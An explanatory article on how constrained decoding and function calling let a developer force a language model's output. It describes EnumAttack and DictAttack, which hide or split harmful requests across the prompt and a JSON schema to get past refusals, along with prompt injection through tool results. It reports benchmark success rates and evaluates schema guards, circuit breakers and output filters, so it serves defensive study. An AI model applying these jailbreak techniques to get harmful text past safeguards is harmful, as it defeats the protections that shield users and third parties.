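# Structured outputs and tool arguments as an attack surface: why closing them may conflict with function calling

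## How structured outputs and function calls work

Structured output is an answer from a language model that must match a format the developer supplies, so that another program can read it reliably. The format is usually a JSON Schema. JSON is a common text notation for data, with named fields inside curly braces, and a JSON Schema lists an object's fields, their types and the values they permit. In function calling, also called tool use, the model writes a request in a fixed format for software to run a named function with arguments the model supplies. Agents, which look things up and change things on a user's behalf, consist largely of a language model making such requests repeatedly.

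Structured outputs and function calls both let the developer constrain what the model can write. These constraints are meant to make the output reliable, but they can also prevent the model from refusing, and a function's arguments can carry a password out of a system as easily as a city name. Both risks result from how a model produces text.

### One token at a time

A language model writes in tokens, which are words or pieces of words from a fixed vocabulary. For each new token, the model reads the prompt and the answer so far and computes a score, called a logit, for every entry in the vocabulary. The softmax function turns the logits into probabilities by raising *e* to the power of each logit and dividing each result by the sum of them all. The server then picks one token at random according to those probabilities, adds it to the text and runs the model again. *When Grammar Guides the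 Attack* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2025) gives the general form of this step, which divides every logit by a temperature setting before the softmax to make the choice more or less random. The example that follows uses a temperature of 1, which has no effect.

Suppose a model would ordinarily decline a request, and only three tokens have any chance of opening its answer. "Sorry" has a logit of 6, an opening brace "{" has 2 and "Sure" has 1. Raising *e* to each logit gives about 403.4, 7.4 and 2.7, which add up to 413.5. Dividing each number by that sum gives its token's probability, so the model opens with "Sorry" about 97.6% of the time, the brace 1.8% and "Sure" 0.7%.

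The first token strongly influences the rest of the response, because the model conditions every later token on it. A response that starts with "Sorry" will most likely continue as a refusal, and one that starts with a brace will most likely continue as a JSON object.

### From a schema to a mask

In *Better Models*, a post about coding agents, Ronacher (2026) distinguishes two ways to get JSON from a model. The developer can ask for valid JSON and check the output, or the server can alter the sampling so that the model never produces invalid JSON. Asking works most of the time. In *Introducing Structured Outputs in the API* (2024), OpenAI reported that a new GPT-4o model scored 93% on the company's own test of complicated schemas with training alone, and 100% when the sampling was also altered.

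The technique behind the second figure is constrained decoding. The server first compiles the schema into a grammar, a set of rules that determine which strings are valid output. OpenAI uses a context-free grammar, which can describe nesting to any depth, because simpler pattern-matchers may fail to match brackets in deeply nested JSON. Compilation takes time (in 2024 OpenAI quoted under ten seconds for a typical new schema and up to a minute for a complex one), so providers keep the result for reuse. According to *Structured outputs*, Anthropic keeps a compiled grammar for 24 hours after its last use.

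As the model generates its answer, a parser works out before each new token which tokens could come next and still allow a valid string to be completed. OpenAI's example is a schema with a single numeric field called "value". An opening brace is valid at the start, but not after the model has written `{"val`. The server therefore needs a new list of valid tokens, called the mask, at every step. As *XGrammar-2* (Li, Dong and colleagues, 2026) describes, the server sets the logit of every other token to minus infinity. Softmax then gives those tokens zero probability, because *e* to the power of minus infinity is zero. Most of the engineering difficulty comes from a mismatch that *Flexible and Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding* (2025) calls token misalignment. A parser works with the symbols of a language, such as a whole keyword, whereas a model's token may cover part of a symbol or several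 symbols.

If the developer has supplied a schema for a JSON object, the grammar allows only the brace out of the three candidates. The mask sets the scores for "Sorry" and "Sure" to minus infinity, so the model cannot begin the refusal. The sum of the powers of *e* falls to 7.4, and the brace's probability becomes 7.4 divided by 7.4, or 100%. In general, an allowed token's new probability is its old one divided by the combined old probability of all the allowed tokens. In this example, the mask makes the brace about 56 times more likely, and the finished JSON does not show that the model had given "Sorry" a probability of 97.6%.

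This is constrained decoding on its own, as someone would get it by running a model with published weights on a private server. Hosted services add a way for the model to refuse. OpenAI gave refusals a separate field in the response, and its current guide, *Structured outputs*, still lists refusals that a program can detect among the feature's benefits. In Anthropic's API, a refusal takes precedence over the schema and is marked by a stop reason in the response. The mask itself does nothing to make a refusal likely, and how often a model refuses when the schema favors a conforming answer has to be measured.

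The mask checks whether the text is valid so far but does not account for how much of the model's probability lies on the valid ways to continue it. *The Parser Already Knows* (Özgü, Wu and colleagues, 2026) illustrates this with strings of five binary digits. Its grammar accepts 00000 and every string that starts with 1, which makes 17 strings, and the model gives all strings the same probability. A sampler faithful to the model would produce each valid string one time in 17. With masking, the model chooses evenly between 0 and 1 at the first step, and after a 0 the mask allows only more zeros, so 00000 comes out half the time. Özgü and colleagues train a small correction that reweights the allowed tokens. Averaged over their grammars, it cut the output's divergence from the faithful distribution by a factor of four to five, on a standard measure. But that distribution also gives zero probability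 to any refusal the grammar excludes, so better sampling of this kind would make structured output more natural without restoring those refusals.

### A function call from definition to result

Anthropic and OpenAI both explain function calling with a weather tool. A cut-down definition of one looks like this:

```json
{
  "name": "get_weather",
  "description": "Look up the temperature in one city.",
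  "input_schema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "city": {"type": "string"},
      "unit": {"enum": ["celsius", "fahrenheit"]}
    },
    "required": ["city", "unit"],
    "additionalProperties": false
  }
}
```

The developer sends this along with a user's question about the weather in San Francisco. Anthropic's *How tool use works* describes the arrangement as a contract in which the developer specifies which operations exist and what shape their inputs take, and the model can only request them. The model never runs anything or receives the code behind the tool. Its reply contains a block with the tool's name, an identifier and an object of arguments, here San Francisco for the city and celsius for the unit.

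The application reads the block and runs its own code, such as a query to a weather service. It then sends a second request, which repeats the conversation so far and adds the result under the same identifier. In Anthropic's *Handle tool calls*, the result is the plain string "15 degrees". The model then writes a sentence for the user or calls another tool, which repeats the process. If the weather service is down, the application can return the error message as the result, and the model will include that information in its reply.

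OpenAI's *Function calling* describes the same loop in five steps and explains that the tool's result is typically a string in whatever format the application chooses, which the model interprets as needed. This is harmless when the result is a temperature, but it matters for security when the tool fetches a web page or opens an email, because the string then contains whatever text whoever wrote it chose to include.

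Anthropic's own servers run some tools, including web search and code execution, and return the results to the model, usually before the application sees anything. A developer can count on inspecting arguments before they take effect only when the application itself runs the tool.

### Strict tool use, forced tool choice and prefill

In the plain version of the loop, only training keeps the model to the schema. Anthropic's *Strict tool use* gives the example of a booking system that expects the number of passengers as an integer but may get the word "two". Strict tool use removes that risk by applying constrained decoding to the arguments, so that they match the tool's schema. The mask can cover just part of the answer. In XGrammar-2, an engine that Li and colleagues have built into the open-source model servers SGLang and vLLM, the model writes ordinary text until it produces the tag that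 opens a call. The engine then applies the grammar for that tool's arguments until they are complete, and switches back to ordinary text. With strict tool use alone, the model in the earlier example could still open with "Sorry" and never call a tool.

Whether to call a tool at all is a separate setting. By default the model decides. Forced tool choice obliges it to call some tool, or one named tool. Anthropic's *Define tools* explains how the company's API brings this about: it writes the opening of the model's answer itself, so that the answer starts with the tool call. The model gives no explanation beforehand, even if the prompt asks for one, and it skips the thinking it might otherwise do. "Sorry" no longer has a place to go. (Anthropic's newest models reject the setting.)

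The API is using a more general technique here called a prefill, in which the developer writes the opening words of the model's answer and the model must continue from them. In an older guide, *Prefill Claude's response for greater output control*, Anthropic recommended prefilling a single opening brace to skip the preamble and go straight to the JSON.

In the toy example, prefilling a brace determines the first token just as the mask does, because the model skips the step where "Sorry" had a 97.6% probability. But a prefill fixes only a few words, so the model could still refuse partway through the object or instead of finishing it, while a mask applies until the grammar is complete. The two also work well together. In *Jev means structured output is interesting again*, Goedecke (2026) suggests prefilling everything up to a field's value and then generating one token from a short list of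 permitted choices, which turns an ordinary model into a fast classifier. Anthropic's JSON outputs don't accept a prefill, so they can't be used this way.

### The data plane and the control plane

Zhang and colleagues sort these mechanisms into two planes. The data plane is the prompt and the text of the answer. The control plane is the set of settings that govern what form an answer may take. Zhang and colleagues apply the second term to grammars, such as a JSON Schema or a regular expression. Tool definitions and tool-choice settings also belong there, because they too determine how an answer can begin and what can fill it. The terms come from computer networking, where a router's control plane works out the routes and its data plane forwards the packets. The distinction is useful to defenders because most filters check prompts and answers but ignore the schema, and attackers have hidden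 harmful requests in schemas for that reason.

The analogy is imperfect because a routing table does not change the contents of packets, whereas a language model receives its schemas as text and can respond to them. Anthropic's API builds a system prompt, the block of instructions that precedes the user's message, from the tool definitions and the developer's own instructions. OpenAI also injects functions into the system message and bills them as input. When a developer requests structured output from Anthropic's API, the API adds an explanation of the format to the prompt. Tool descriptions do not affect the grammar, but Anthropic calls detailed descriptions "by far the most important factor in tool performance".

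A schema therefore has two roles: it supplies the rules for the mask, and the model reads it as text. A constraint can move from one role to the other. For example, Anthropic's grammars do not support a minimum value for a number, so most of the company's software libraries remove the minimum from the schema and write it into the field's description, where the model may or may not follow it.

The grammar and the model's output also affect each other. Any string that the grammar forces into the answer becomes part of the text on which the model conditions its next token. In XGrammar-2, when the model's free text spells out a tool's tag, that tag determines which grammar applies next. Ronacher calls tool calls "rather crude in-band signalling", meaning that commands and content travel in the same stream.

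### What function calling needs

A defence that closes some of these openings must also keep function calling working, so it has to meet four requirements.

Schemas have to arrive with the request. Developers usually declare their functions in each API call, and the list can change between calls because an application may have hundreds of tools and show each user only the permitted ones. Li and colleagues measured how often compiled grammars could be reused, with a pool of 1,908 tools and batches of 100 requests. When every request used the same tools, the engine could reuse a whole grammar 99% of the time. When each request drew its own random set, it could never reuse a whole grammar, although smaller parts did recur. Random draws surely overstate the variety of real traffic, where one application sends much the same tools all day. Still, a provider that serves the public cannot accept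 only schemas from an approved list, since any new customer may bring one that nobody has seen.

Arguments also have to reach the function exactly as the model wrote them. The editing tool in Ronacher's post, for example, finds one exact string in a file and replaces it with another. If something between the model and the tool drops a space or changes a quotation mark, the old string no longer matches and the edit fails. Anthropic therefore instructs the model in its tool-use prompt to give strings as they are, and warns that spaces will be preserved. A filter that rewrites suspicious arguments would break legitimate calls of this sort.

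Some fields require free text. An enum, a schema's list of permitted values, works for a temperature unit. OpenAI advises developers to use enums where they can, and not to have the model fill in arguments the application already knows, such as the number of an order the user has just selected. Both practices limit what an attacker can manipulate. But no list could contain every email a user might want to send, and OpenAI's custom tools even accept arbitrary strings, such as Python programs. The grammar can guarantee that the body of an email is a string, but it can't check whether that string contains a greeting or a customer's bank details.

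The last requirement is that calls are guaranteed to match the schema. When Ronacher continued one user's long coding session with Claude Opus 4.8, then one of Anthropic's newest models, about 20% of its calls to the editing tool were invalid. In the calls he inspected, the replacement text was correct, but the model had added fields that are not in the schema. Strict tool use eliminated the errors in his runs. A fresh one-line request did not reproduce the problem, so the 20% figure is not an estimate of how often models fail in general. Anthropic's older models did not make this mistake, which is evidence against the hope that better models will make constrained decoding unnecessary. Ronacher guesses that the newer models were trained in an environment that silently repairs malformed calls, and so learned that extra fields do no harm.

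Anthropic lists refusals, answers that hit the length limit, and enum values returned with different capitalization as exceptions to the guarantee. It also accepts at most 20 strict tools per request, so an agent with hundreds of tools gets the guarantee for only some of them.

### Three attackers

The developer who holds the API key controls everything in the request: the prompt, the schemas, the tool definitions, the tool choice and, where the API still accepts one, the prefill. A malicious developer wants text that the model would otherwise refuse to write, and the model's provider is responsible for preventing that. Such a developer doesn't need the function-calling loop to continue after the model has written the arguments. Because the model never receives a tool's code, the developer can define a tool that doesn't exist and take the harmful text from its arguments.

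The end user of an application normally reaches only the data plane, through a chat box or a form, because the developer has already fixed the schemas. The user may want the application's hidden instructions, another customer's records or an action it should not take. In this case, the developer needs protection from the user. The case is less clear when an application builds schemas from user input, for example by letting customers name the columns of a report, because the user then writes a small part of the control plane.

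An attacker doesn't need an account to put instructions in a web page or email that an agent reads. The instructions reach the model in a tool result, and if the model follows them, it may copy private data into the arguments of its next call. This attack is called prompt injection, and its victims are both the developer and the user.

A defence against one of these people may do nothing about another. If a provider withdraws forced tool choice, a malicious developer can no longer use it, but someone attacking through a web page never had access to it. A guard model, a separate model that checks for harmful content, will find nothing wrong with the schemas of an honest application whose agent has just opened a poisoned email. A filter on outgoing arguments might stop that agent from sending the data, but if the filter runs in the developer's own code, a malicious developer can leave it out.

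## Harmful requests carried in an output schema

A schema can dictate some of an answer's words as well as its shape. *When Grammar Guides the Attack* (Zhang and colleagues, first posted in March 2025 and published at the ACM CCS security conference in 2026) describes a way to use this to jailbreak a model, that is, to get it to write what it was trained to refuse. Zhang and colleagues call the method a constrained decoding attack. The attacker sends an innocent-looking prompt, hides some or all of a harmful request in the schema, and reads the answer in the returned JSON.

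### Forced text, then free text

In this attack, the schema first forces a piece of text into the model's answer, and the model then continues from that text in its own words.

A travel site could do the same thing harmlessly. Suppose it asks a model for advice on a winter holiday, using a schema with two fields. The first field allows only the sentence "Lisbon is the best choice for a winter holiday, for three reasons." The second accepts any string. The model might otherwise have recommended Madeira or asked about the budget, but the mask allows only tokens that spell out the Lisbon sentence in the first field. The model therefore writes that sentence every time, even if it would have written it only one time in a million without the schema.

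In the free field, the mask allows almost any text, so the model's own probabilities again largely determine what it writes. But the model is now continuing an answer that already recommends Lisbon, so it will most likely give three reasons for going there. The grammar would also let it write that, on reflection, Madeira would be better, but the model is unlikely to do so.

An attacker uses the mask to force a sentence in which the model appears to accept a harmful request. The model then supplies the harmful details itself, because they are what would normally come next.

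On the paper's project page, Zhang and colleagues write that internal safety alignment, the training that teaches a model to refuse, cannot stop the attack alone. This is true of the forced text, because training has no effect when the mask leaves only one option. The claim seems too strong for the free text, where a model could learn to decline inside the string. Some of the paper's measurements suggest that one model partly does this.

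### A request kept whole or divided

Zhang and colleagues built two forms of the attack. One, EnumAttack, puts the whole request into the schema's enums, the lists of permitted values, so the prompt itself can be harmless. A filter that checks only prompts would find nothing to flag, even though the request is written in plain words in the schema.

DictAttack avoids this by splitting the request between the prompt and the schema so that neither half looks harmful. A harmless request could be split the same way, with a prompt that asks for a recipe without naming the dish and a schema that names the dish without mentioning cooking. The complete request appears only when the model combines the halves in its answer, after a filter that inspected each half separately has passed both.

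A model could still stop if it noticed what it was assembling. *Do Reasoning LLMs Refuse What They Infer in Long Contexts?* (2026) tests a related ability, without schemas, by making models reconstruct a harmful aim from fragments. One 7-billion-parameter reasoning model with extra safety training responded safely every time it only had to retrieve the request, but 82.3% of the time when it had to infer the aim. The extra training also raised its refusal rate on harmless requests from 1.6% to 41.2%. Results from a model that small are weak evidence about GPT-5, but the gap suggests that dividing a request weakens refusal even before a schema forces any text.

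The attacker needs control of the schema, which anyone with an API key has. The experiments assume an attacker who calls the API and supplies the schema directly. Zhang and colleagues also list less direct routes, such as a compromised agent backend or a malicious tool offered through the Model Context Protocol, a standard for loading tools into agents from outside servers. With a malicious tool, an outsider without the developer's key writes part of the control plane.

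Both forms use fixed values and free strings, which legitimate function calls also need. A provider could refuse schemas that fix a whole sentence, but then a support tool could no longer choose among approved replies, and a harmful request split into innocuous pieces might not need a whole sentence in any one place. Banning either feature would do far more harm than the attack does, so a defence has to work out what the strings in a schema mean.

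### Success rates without schema filters

The final paper covers 13 models, some proprietary and some with published weights, and five standard benchmarks of harmful requests. A language model judges whether each answer is harmful. With nothing checking the schemas, EnumAttack succeeded 95.8% of the time on average against mainstream models. DictAttack succeeded between 94.3% and 99.5% of the time against four flagship models: GPT-5, Gemini 2.5 Pro, DeepSeek-R1 and gpt-oss-120b, a model whose weights OpenAI has published. (Even basic checks on the schema reduce EnumAttack's success, and DictAttack holds up better.)

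The paper's first version, *Output Constraints as Attack Surface* (Zhang, Zhao and colleagues, 2025), compares EnumAttack with simply asking. On AdvBench, a list of 520 harmful requests, GPT-4o gave 489 short refusals and 25 longer ones when the requests came as ordinary prompts, and complied to some degree with six. When the same requests came through the schema, it complied with all 520. Averaged over all five benchmarks, the results were:

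| Model | Success when asked directly | Success with EnumAttack | StrongREJECT score with EnumAttack |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 15.2% | 99.2% | 88.9% |
| GPT-4o mini | 22.3% | 98.1% | 85.0% |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 24.2% | 90.1% | 82.8% |
| Phi-3.5-MoE | 22.2% | 97.4% | 73.7% |

The four success rates for EnumAttack, the plain attack, average 96.2%. The abstract of that version wrongly attributes this figure to a more elaborate variant.

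The last column gives the StrongREJECT score, which measures how useful the harmful answer was. A refusal scores zero, and any other answer scores the mean of two ratings from 0 to 1, for how specific and how convincing it is. An attack that yields vague or useless text will therefore have a high success rate but a low StrongREJECT score. The two measures are fairly close on GPT-4o but nearly 24 points apart on Phi-3.5-MoE, a Microsoft model with published weights, so that model often complied without giving much useful information. DictAttack scored 0.98 on Gemini 2.5 Pro.

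In the first version, GPT-4o was both the judge and one of the targets. Under the standard StrongREJECT procedure, it declined to judge more than 20% of the cases because the material was too offensive. Zhang and colleagues then forced its verdicts into a schema, after which it never declined. This fix relies on the weakness they were studying. A judge that can't decline has to give a verdict on those cases too, and that verdict may be wrong. Such errors could explain a difference of a few percentage points between models, but hardly a rise from 15.2% to 99.2%.

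To grade the answers, Zhang and colleagues had to put harmful questions and answers inside a schema themselves. So a provider that rejected every schema containing harmful text would block this kind of safety research, along with any moderation service that works the same way.

### Filters, training and serving engines

The comparison in the table changes two things at once, because EnumAttack moves the request out of the prompt, where a provider's filter might catch it, and forces the model to begin by agreeing. Zhang and colleagues guess that GPT-4o's short, uniform refusals come from a filter outside the model, but nobody outside OpenAI can check. It would be hard to tell from the hosted models alone whether the attack had defeated a filter, the model's training, or both.

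Models with published weights help here because researchers can run them privately, without a provider's filter. The first version tested five of them on the AdvBench requests, using the open-source engine vLLM. EnumAttack succeeded at least 98.7% of the time on every model. StrongREJECT scores were about 95% or higher for four of the models and 76.9% for Phi-3.5-MoE. So the attack gets past the models' training as well as the filters.

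In these runs, EnumAttack also worked across serving engines. It succeeded on those of OpenAI and Google, which don't publish how they implement structured output, and on vLLM, whose code is open. This is the expected result if the cause is the masking step itself, which any engine must carry out in some form to guarantee valid output. A bug in one company's parser would have produced more uneven results. Gemini 2.0 Flash resisted somewhat better than the other models, with the attack's lowest success rate against it on any benchmark being 81.2%, but a difference that size could as easily come from the model as from the engine.

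### How the probability of refusal shifts

Success rates show that refusals disappear but not what replaces them. To find out, Zhang and colleagues looked at the token probabilities of Phi-3.5-MoE, the most resistant of the open-weight models they tested. They used beam search, which follows several of the most probable continuations instead of sampling one, and sorted the response openings into refusals, harmless content, and weakly or strongly harmful content.

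When asked directly, the model put nearly all the probability on refusal. Adding an agreeable phrase to the prompt made almost no difference. Requiring JSON, with no harmful text in the format, cut the probability of refusal by about half, though the model still mostly refused. Honest developers who require an ordinary format can therefore make a model less likely to refuse without intending to.

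EnumAttack eliminated direct refusals, but much of the probability moved to harmless continuations, in which the model followed the format but filled it with safe content. A benign system prompt made these continuations less likely. Zhang and colleagues then tried a variant that forces the model to start with the beginning of a harmful answer from another model with weaker safeguards. With this variant, the five most probable continuations were all strongly harmful.

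The variant raised Phi-3.5-MoE's average StrongREJECT score from 73.7% to 83.0%, with GPT-4o supplying the forced text. Some of that gain may come from GPT-4o's text rather than from weaker caution. The text already contains part of an answer, which gives Phi-3.5-MoE information it might have lacked and may itself have raised the judge's score. The probabilities are better evidence of weaker caution because they show what the model itself would write next, but they come from one model, and the exact percentages may well differ for others.

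### Why guarding the first few tokens fails

In ordinary use, a refusal depends mostly on its opening, such as the "Sorry" in the earlier toy example. Training can therefore make a model look very safe by changing little more than the first few tokens of its responses. Zhang and colleagues call this shallow safety alignment, a term from earlier work by Xiangyu Qi and others.

Safety training typically makes a model more likely to refuse a harmful prompt, but it may do much less to make the model refuse once its answer has already agreed to help. If training examples nearly always show the refusal at the beginning, the model is rarely trained to refuse partway through an answer, which is what it would have to do after the forced text. Zhang and colleagues express this as an inequality in which a harmful token is far more probable after the forced text than after the text the model would have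 written by itself.

The Lisbon example has the same structure. A model might strongly prefer Madeira and say so in its first sentence every time, yet still give three good reasons for Lisbon when the schema replaces that sentence, because it expresses the preference only there.

Phi-3.5-MoE's lower scores suggest that training can affect more of the answer than its opening. Zhang and colleagues interpret the scores as a sign of deeper alignment, which would explain why the model kept producing harmless content after the forced agreement. Weaker general ability, including less knowledge of the subjects, is probably not the main reason, because two small models, Llama 3.1 8B and Gemma 2 9B, scored about 95% on the same AdvBench requests.

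Like a schema, a prefill exploits shallow alignment by making the model continue from a statement it would not have chosen. But a schema can fix text at any point in the answer, including after the model has written freely. The model can abandon a prefilled sentence and refuse in ordinary prose, but under a schema it has to fit the refusal inside a string field, and the receiving program receives a valid object whether or not the model refuses.

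A prefill is part of the conversation, so a filter that scans the messages can scan it too, but a schema is sent in a separate part of the request. A provider that withdraws prefill but still accepts arbitrary enums has therefore closed only one way of dictating part of the model's output.

### Newer models and Claude

The proprietary models in the first version were from 2024 and early 2025, and the four flagship models in the final version are from 2025. OpenAI and Google have released newer models since. DictAttack's success on GPT-5 is evidence that another generation of safety training did not fix the problem, but it can't show how the latest models behave.

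The conference's reviewers gave the paper a "Results Reproduced" badge, which means that people other than the authors obtained its main results with the authors' materials. This makes an error in the original runs less likely, but it does not show that the results hold for other models, and a rerun with the same judge would repeat the judge's mistakes.

The independent evidence on 2026 models is indirect. The closest comes from a different Zhang and colleagues at Tsinghua University and the University of Electronic Science and Technology of China. *Grammar-Constrained Decoding Can Jailbreak LLMs into Generating Malicious Code* (Zhang, Lu and Li, 2026) reports that merely requiring valid Python raised the average success rate of malicious coding requests from 22.0% to 67.4% on five models behind commercial APIs, including GPT-5 and the 2026 model MiniMax-M2.7. The grammar contained no part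 of the request, so the study does not replicate EnumAttack or DictAttack, but it does confirm that removing ordinary refusals from the permitted output has a large effect.

Zhang, Lu and Li also reran an older attack, AttackPrefixTree, which builds a grammar for each request by repeatedly querying the model. On the same five models it reached only 27.7%, barely above asking directly. They suggest that jailbreaks designed for general misuse often reduce code quality, which would partly explain the low result. Still, controlling the grammar does not guarantee success, and it would be unwise to assume the 94.3–99.5% range holds for other models and tasks without testing.

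Forced formats also weaken refusal in multiple-choice questions. *When Choices Become Risks* (2026) finds that the 14 models it covers often refuse less when every option is unsafe and none is a refusal. This again suggests that the cause is the restricted answer rather than some detail of JSON.

Zhang and colleagues tested no Claude models, because Anthropic's API did not offer schema-constrained output at the time. It does now, and two of its features could help. It gives precedence to refusals, and it adds an explanation of the format to the prompt, which gives the model some chance to recognize a harmful request before it writes anything. Neither feature guarantees that the model will refuse, and DictAttack in particular depends on the request not looking harmful beforehand. We can't tell from the published success rates whether Claude is safe or vulnerable.

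### What followed disclosure

Zhang and colleagues reported the vulnerability to OpenAI and Google in early 2025, and the agreed period of secrecy has since ended. They can't see what either company has changed internally, and they warn readers not to assume that any particular endpoint is patched. Assuming that an endpoint is still vulnerable would be equally unsafe, because the provider can start checking schemas before they reach a model without changing the model's name. The same test could therefore give a different result today, even on a dated checkpoint such as the November 2024 version of GPT-4o.

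They also notified the maintainers of the XGrammar engine, who acknowledged the issue. XGrammar has had more ordinary security problems too. The vulnerability database run by NIST, the US standards agency, lists one in which the engine allocated resources without limit, which let an attacker overload a server. The maintainers fixed it in version 0.1.24.

Constrained decoding attacks are hard for the decoding engine's developers to fix because the engine is working correctly, producing valid output from a valid schema. To stop an attack, the engine would have to detect harmful strings in the schema, including strings that are harmful only when combined with a prompt it may never receive. Anyone running the engine on a private server could also remove the check. That leaves prevention to the companies that train the models, and to those that host them and can read the prompt and schema together.

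## What schema filters and model-level defences catch

Filters already check prompts, so the obvious fix is to have them check schemas too. Zhang and colleagues tested filters that do this, filters that read the prompt and schema together, and a model given extra training to avoid harmful answers.

### Guards that read the schema

They used three guards: Llama Guard 3 8B, a small classifier from Meta; OpenAI's moderation service; and GPT-4o, prompted to act as an auditor. The table gives the share of attacks using AdvBench requests that each guard flagged. EnumAttack leaves the request readable in the schema, while DictAttack splits it between the schema and the prompt. An attacker can also add harmless words to a DictAttack schema so that the revealing ones stand out less.

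| What the guard read | Attack | Llama Guard | Moderation service | GPT-4o |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Schema | EnumAttack | 97.7% | 90.2% | 100.0% |
| Schema | DictAttack, undiluted | 6.5% | 0.0% | 17.7% |
| Schema | DictAttack, lightly diluted | 1.7% | 0.0% | 8.1% |
| Schema | DictAttack, heavily diluted | 1.5% | 0.0% | 5.3% |
| Prompt and schema | DictAttack | 28.6% | 0.2% | 24.2% |
| Prompt and schema | DictAttack, halves in separate turns | 1.5% | 0.0% | 5.3% |

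Checking the schema is enough to stop most EnumAttack attempts. Across three mainstream models and five benchmarks, Llama Guard cut the attack's average success rate from 95.8% to 7.9%. On GPT-4o, the attack succeeded about 8% of the time with this defence, compared with 15.2% for direct requests.

The guard did less well on SorryBench, another of the five benchmarks. GPT-4o's rate there fell from 96.4% to 16.6%, which implies the guard caught about 83% of the requests. GPT-4o complied with a third of the SorryBench requests when asked directly, so many of them are probably less blatant than AdvBench's. Real traffic presumably contains many such requests, so a provider shouldn't count on the guard catching 97.7% of harmful requests.

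The same guard barely reduced DictAttack's success rate on the four flagship models, from 94.3–99.5% to 92.7–97.8%. GPT-4o detected more than Llama Guard did, but heavy dilution removed most of that advantage.

### Reading both halves together

A guard with the prompt and the schema in front of it has everything it needs to spot a divided request. GPT-4o still caught only 24.2%, using an audit prompt adapted from an earlier defence called SelfDefend. This is where the paper's headline figure comes from, that DictAttack keeps a 75.8% success rate against the best guards. Because the guard runs separately from the model, Zhang and colleagues calculate the result instead of measuring it:

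success with the guard = (1 − detection rate) × success without it

If the attack succeeds about 100% of the time without a guard, a 24.2% detection rate lowers its success rate to (1 − 0.242) × 100% = 75.8%. The attack's actual success rate against GPT-5 on AdvBench was 96.0%, which would give 72.8%. Llama Guard's 28.6% detection rate would lower the 75.8% to 71.4%. Zhang and colleagues also write that SelfDefend's best strategy detects 18.5% of the attacks, which would mean 81.5% success, and they don't reconcile this with the 24.2%. Either way, the joint guard misses at least seven attacks in ten.

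The DictAttack paper attributes the failure to complexity, arguing that language models can't reliably audit modern schemas across both planes. Its own results count against this. DictAttack works only if the target model reassembles the request, and GPT-4o complied with 99.8% of the AdvBench requests as a target, so it can read these schemas. As an auditor, it flagged 24.2%. It seems more likely that the auditor didn't reassemble the request, since the attacker's prompt tells the target to do so and the audit prompt asks for a verdict. A guard that first wrote out what the answer would contain and then judged it might catch far more, but it would cost roughly as much as running the model twice.

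### Halves that arrive in separate turns

Guards usually check one request at a time. In a variant of DictAttack, the attacker sends the prompt's half of the attack early in a conversation and the schema's half in a later request, so no single check covers both. Detection fell to 5.3% or less with every guard. The three figures are identical to those for the schema-only guards under heavy dilution, so Zhang and colleagues may have reused them because a guard in this position receives only the schema. That reasoning is sound, but the figures shouldn't count as independent evidence.

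The remedy is for the guard to read the whole conversation every time. An application normally resends the conversation with each tool result, so the guard has the text, but the total amount it must read grows quickly. If an agent makes 50 requests and each adds 2,000 tokens, checking only the new material means reading 100,000 tokens, while rereading everything each time means reading 2,000 × (1 + 2 + … + 50), or 2.55 million, about 25 times as many. Zhang and colleagues call this impractical, both for this reason and because the guard would need as long a context window as the model it protects and would have to find a few words buried dozens of turns back.

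Having a guard read the history may be better described as expensive. The protected model has to process the same history, and providers reduce that cost by caching. Anthropic's *API and data retention* describes a prompt cache that keeps the model's processed form of a prompt in memory for a limited time, and a guard could use the same technique.

Providers that keep records can also check conversations afterwards. Anthropic requires 30-day retention for its Covered Models (Fable and Mythos models from version 5 on), and its automated safety systems assess the retained data. A later review can cover an entire conversation without delaying tool calls. It comes too late to stop the first harmful answer, but it could identify an account that keeps trying.

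### Circuit breakers

Circuit breakers use extra training to change how a model represents harmful content. When the model starts to produce such content, the training diverts its internal state, so it writes something else. This should help against schema attacks, because the defence doesn't depend on how the answer begins.

Zhang and colleagues had no flagship model with this training, so they compared two public versions of Llama 3 8B on 50 AdvBench requests. They ran their own attacks and AutoDAN-Turbo, which automatically searches for ways to frame a harmful prompt, and then combined AutoDAN-Turbo with EnumAttack's schema.

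| Attack | Ordinary model | With circuit breakers |
|---|---|---|
| AutoDAN-Turbo (prompt only) | 82% | 6% |
| EnumAttack (schema only) | 84% | 32% |
| DictAttack | 24% | 14% |
| AutoDAN-Turbo with EnumAttack | 94% | 78% |

We can learn little from the DictAttack row, because an 8-billion-parameter model often fails to reassemble the request even without a defence. The fall from 84% to 32% is a real improvement, and 50 requests are enough to establish it.

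The combined attack succeeded 78% of the time. If the two attacks succeeded independently, an attacker who tried both on every request would succeed 1 − (0.94 × 0.68), or 36%, of the time, so each attack makes the other more effective. Zhang and colleagues suggest that AutoDAN's framing keeps the harmful internal state from forming, and the grammar then commits the model to a step-by-step answer. The success rates are consistent with this explanation but can't confirm it on their own.

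Constrained decoding also weakens the defence directly, because the mask blocks the end-of-text token until the JSON object is complete. A model that would otherwise stop partway through its answer can at best fill the remaining fields with degraded text.

The breaker seems to do little harm to function calling. On 50 ordinary schemas from each of four difficulty levels, the share of valid outputs stayed at 84% on two levels, fell from 76% to 74% on one, and rose from 48% to 54% on the hardest. (Zhang and colleagues describe all the changes as two points or less, but the last was six points, or three schemas.) However, the test measured only whether the output matched the schema, so it would miss valid JSON with worse values in it. Ordinary schemas from GitHub are also a poor guide to what happens when a security scanner's legitimate output triggers the breaker.

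### Filters that read the finished answer

When a request is divided between the planes, its parts come together in the model's answer. Any dangerous instructions the attacker wants must also appear there, so a filter that reads the answer can largely ignore which plane carried each part of the request, provided it checks string fields and tool arguments as carefully as chat.

Zhang and colleagues object that output filters add latency and cost, and they report that major APIs such as OpenAI's and Gemini's often omit them. Latency matters less for structured outputs than in a chat window, because a program generally can't use a JSON object until it is complete. Anthropic, for example, tells Java developers who stream structured outputs to collect the full response before converting it. Holding the output back until it is complete doesn't delay such a program. Running the filter still adds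 a delay, which an agent incurs at every call.

They also argue that no output filter can get every case right. Their example is an attack whose output has the same form as that of a legitimate safety audit, in which a model grades a harmful question and answer it is given. If the two outputs are the same, a filter that sees only outputs must either block the audit or let the attack through.

The argument holds for a filter that checks only the answer. But an audit repeats harmful text already in the request, while an attacker wants the model to write new harmful text. A filter that could compare the answer with the prompt and schema could therefore often distinguish quoted text from new text. Zhang and colleagues propose a similar defence that tracks where each token came from. They also propose keeping certain refusal tokens available under any grammar.

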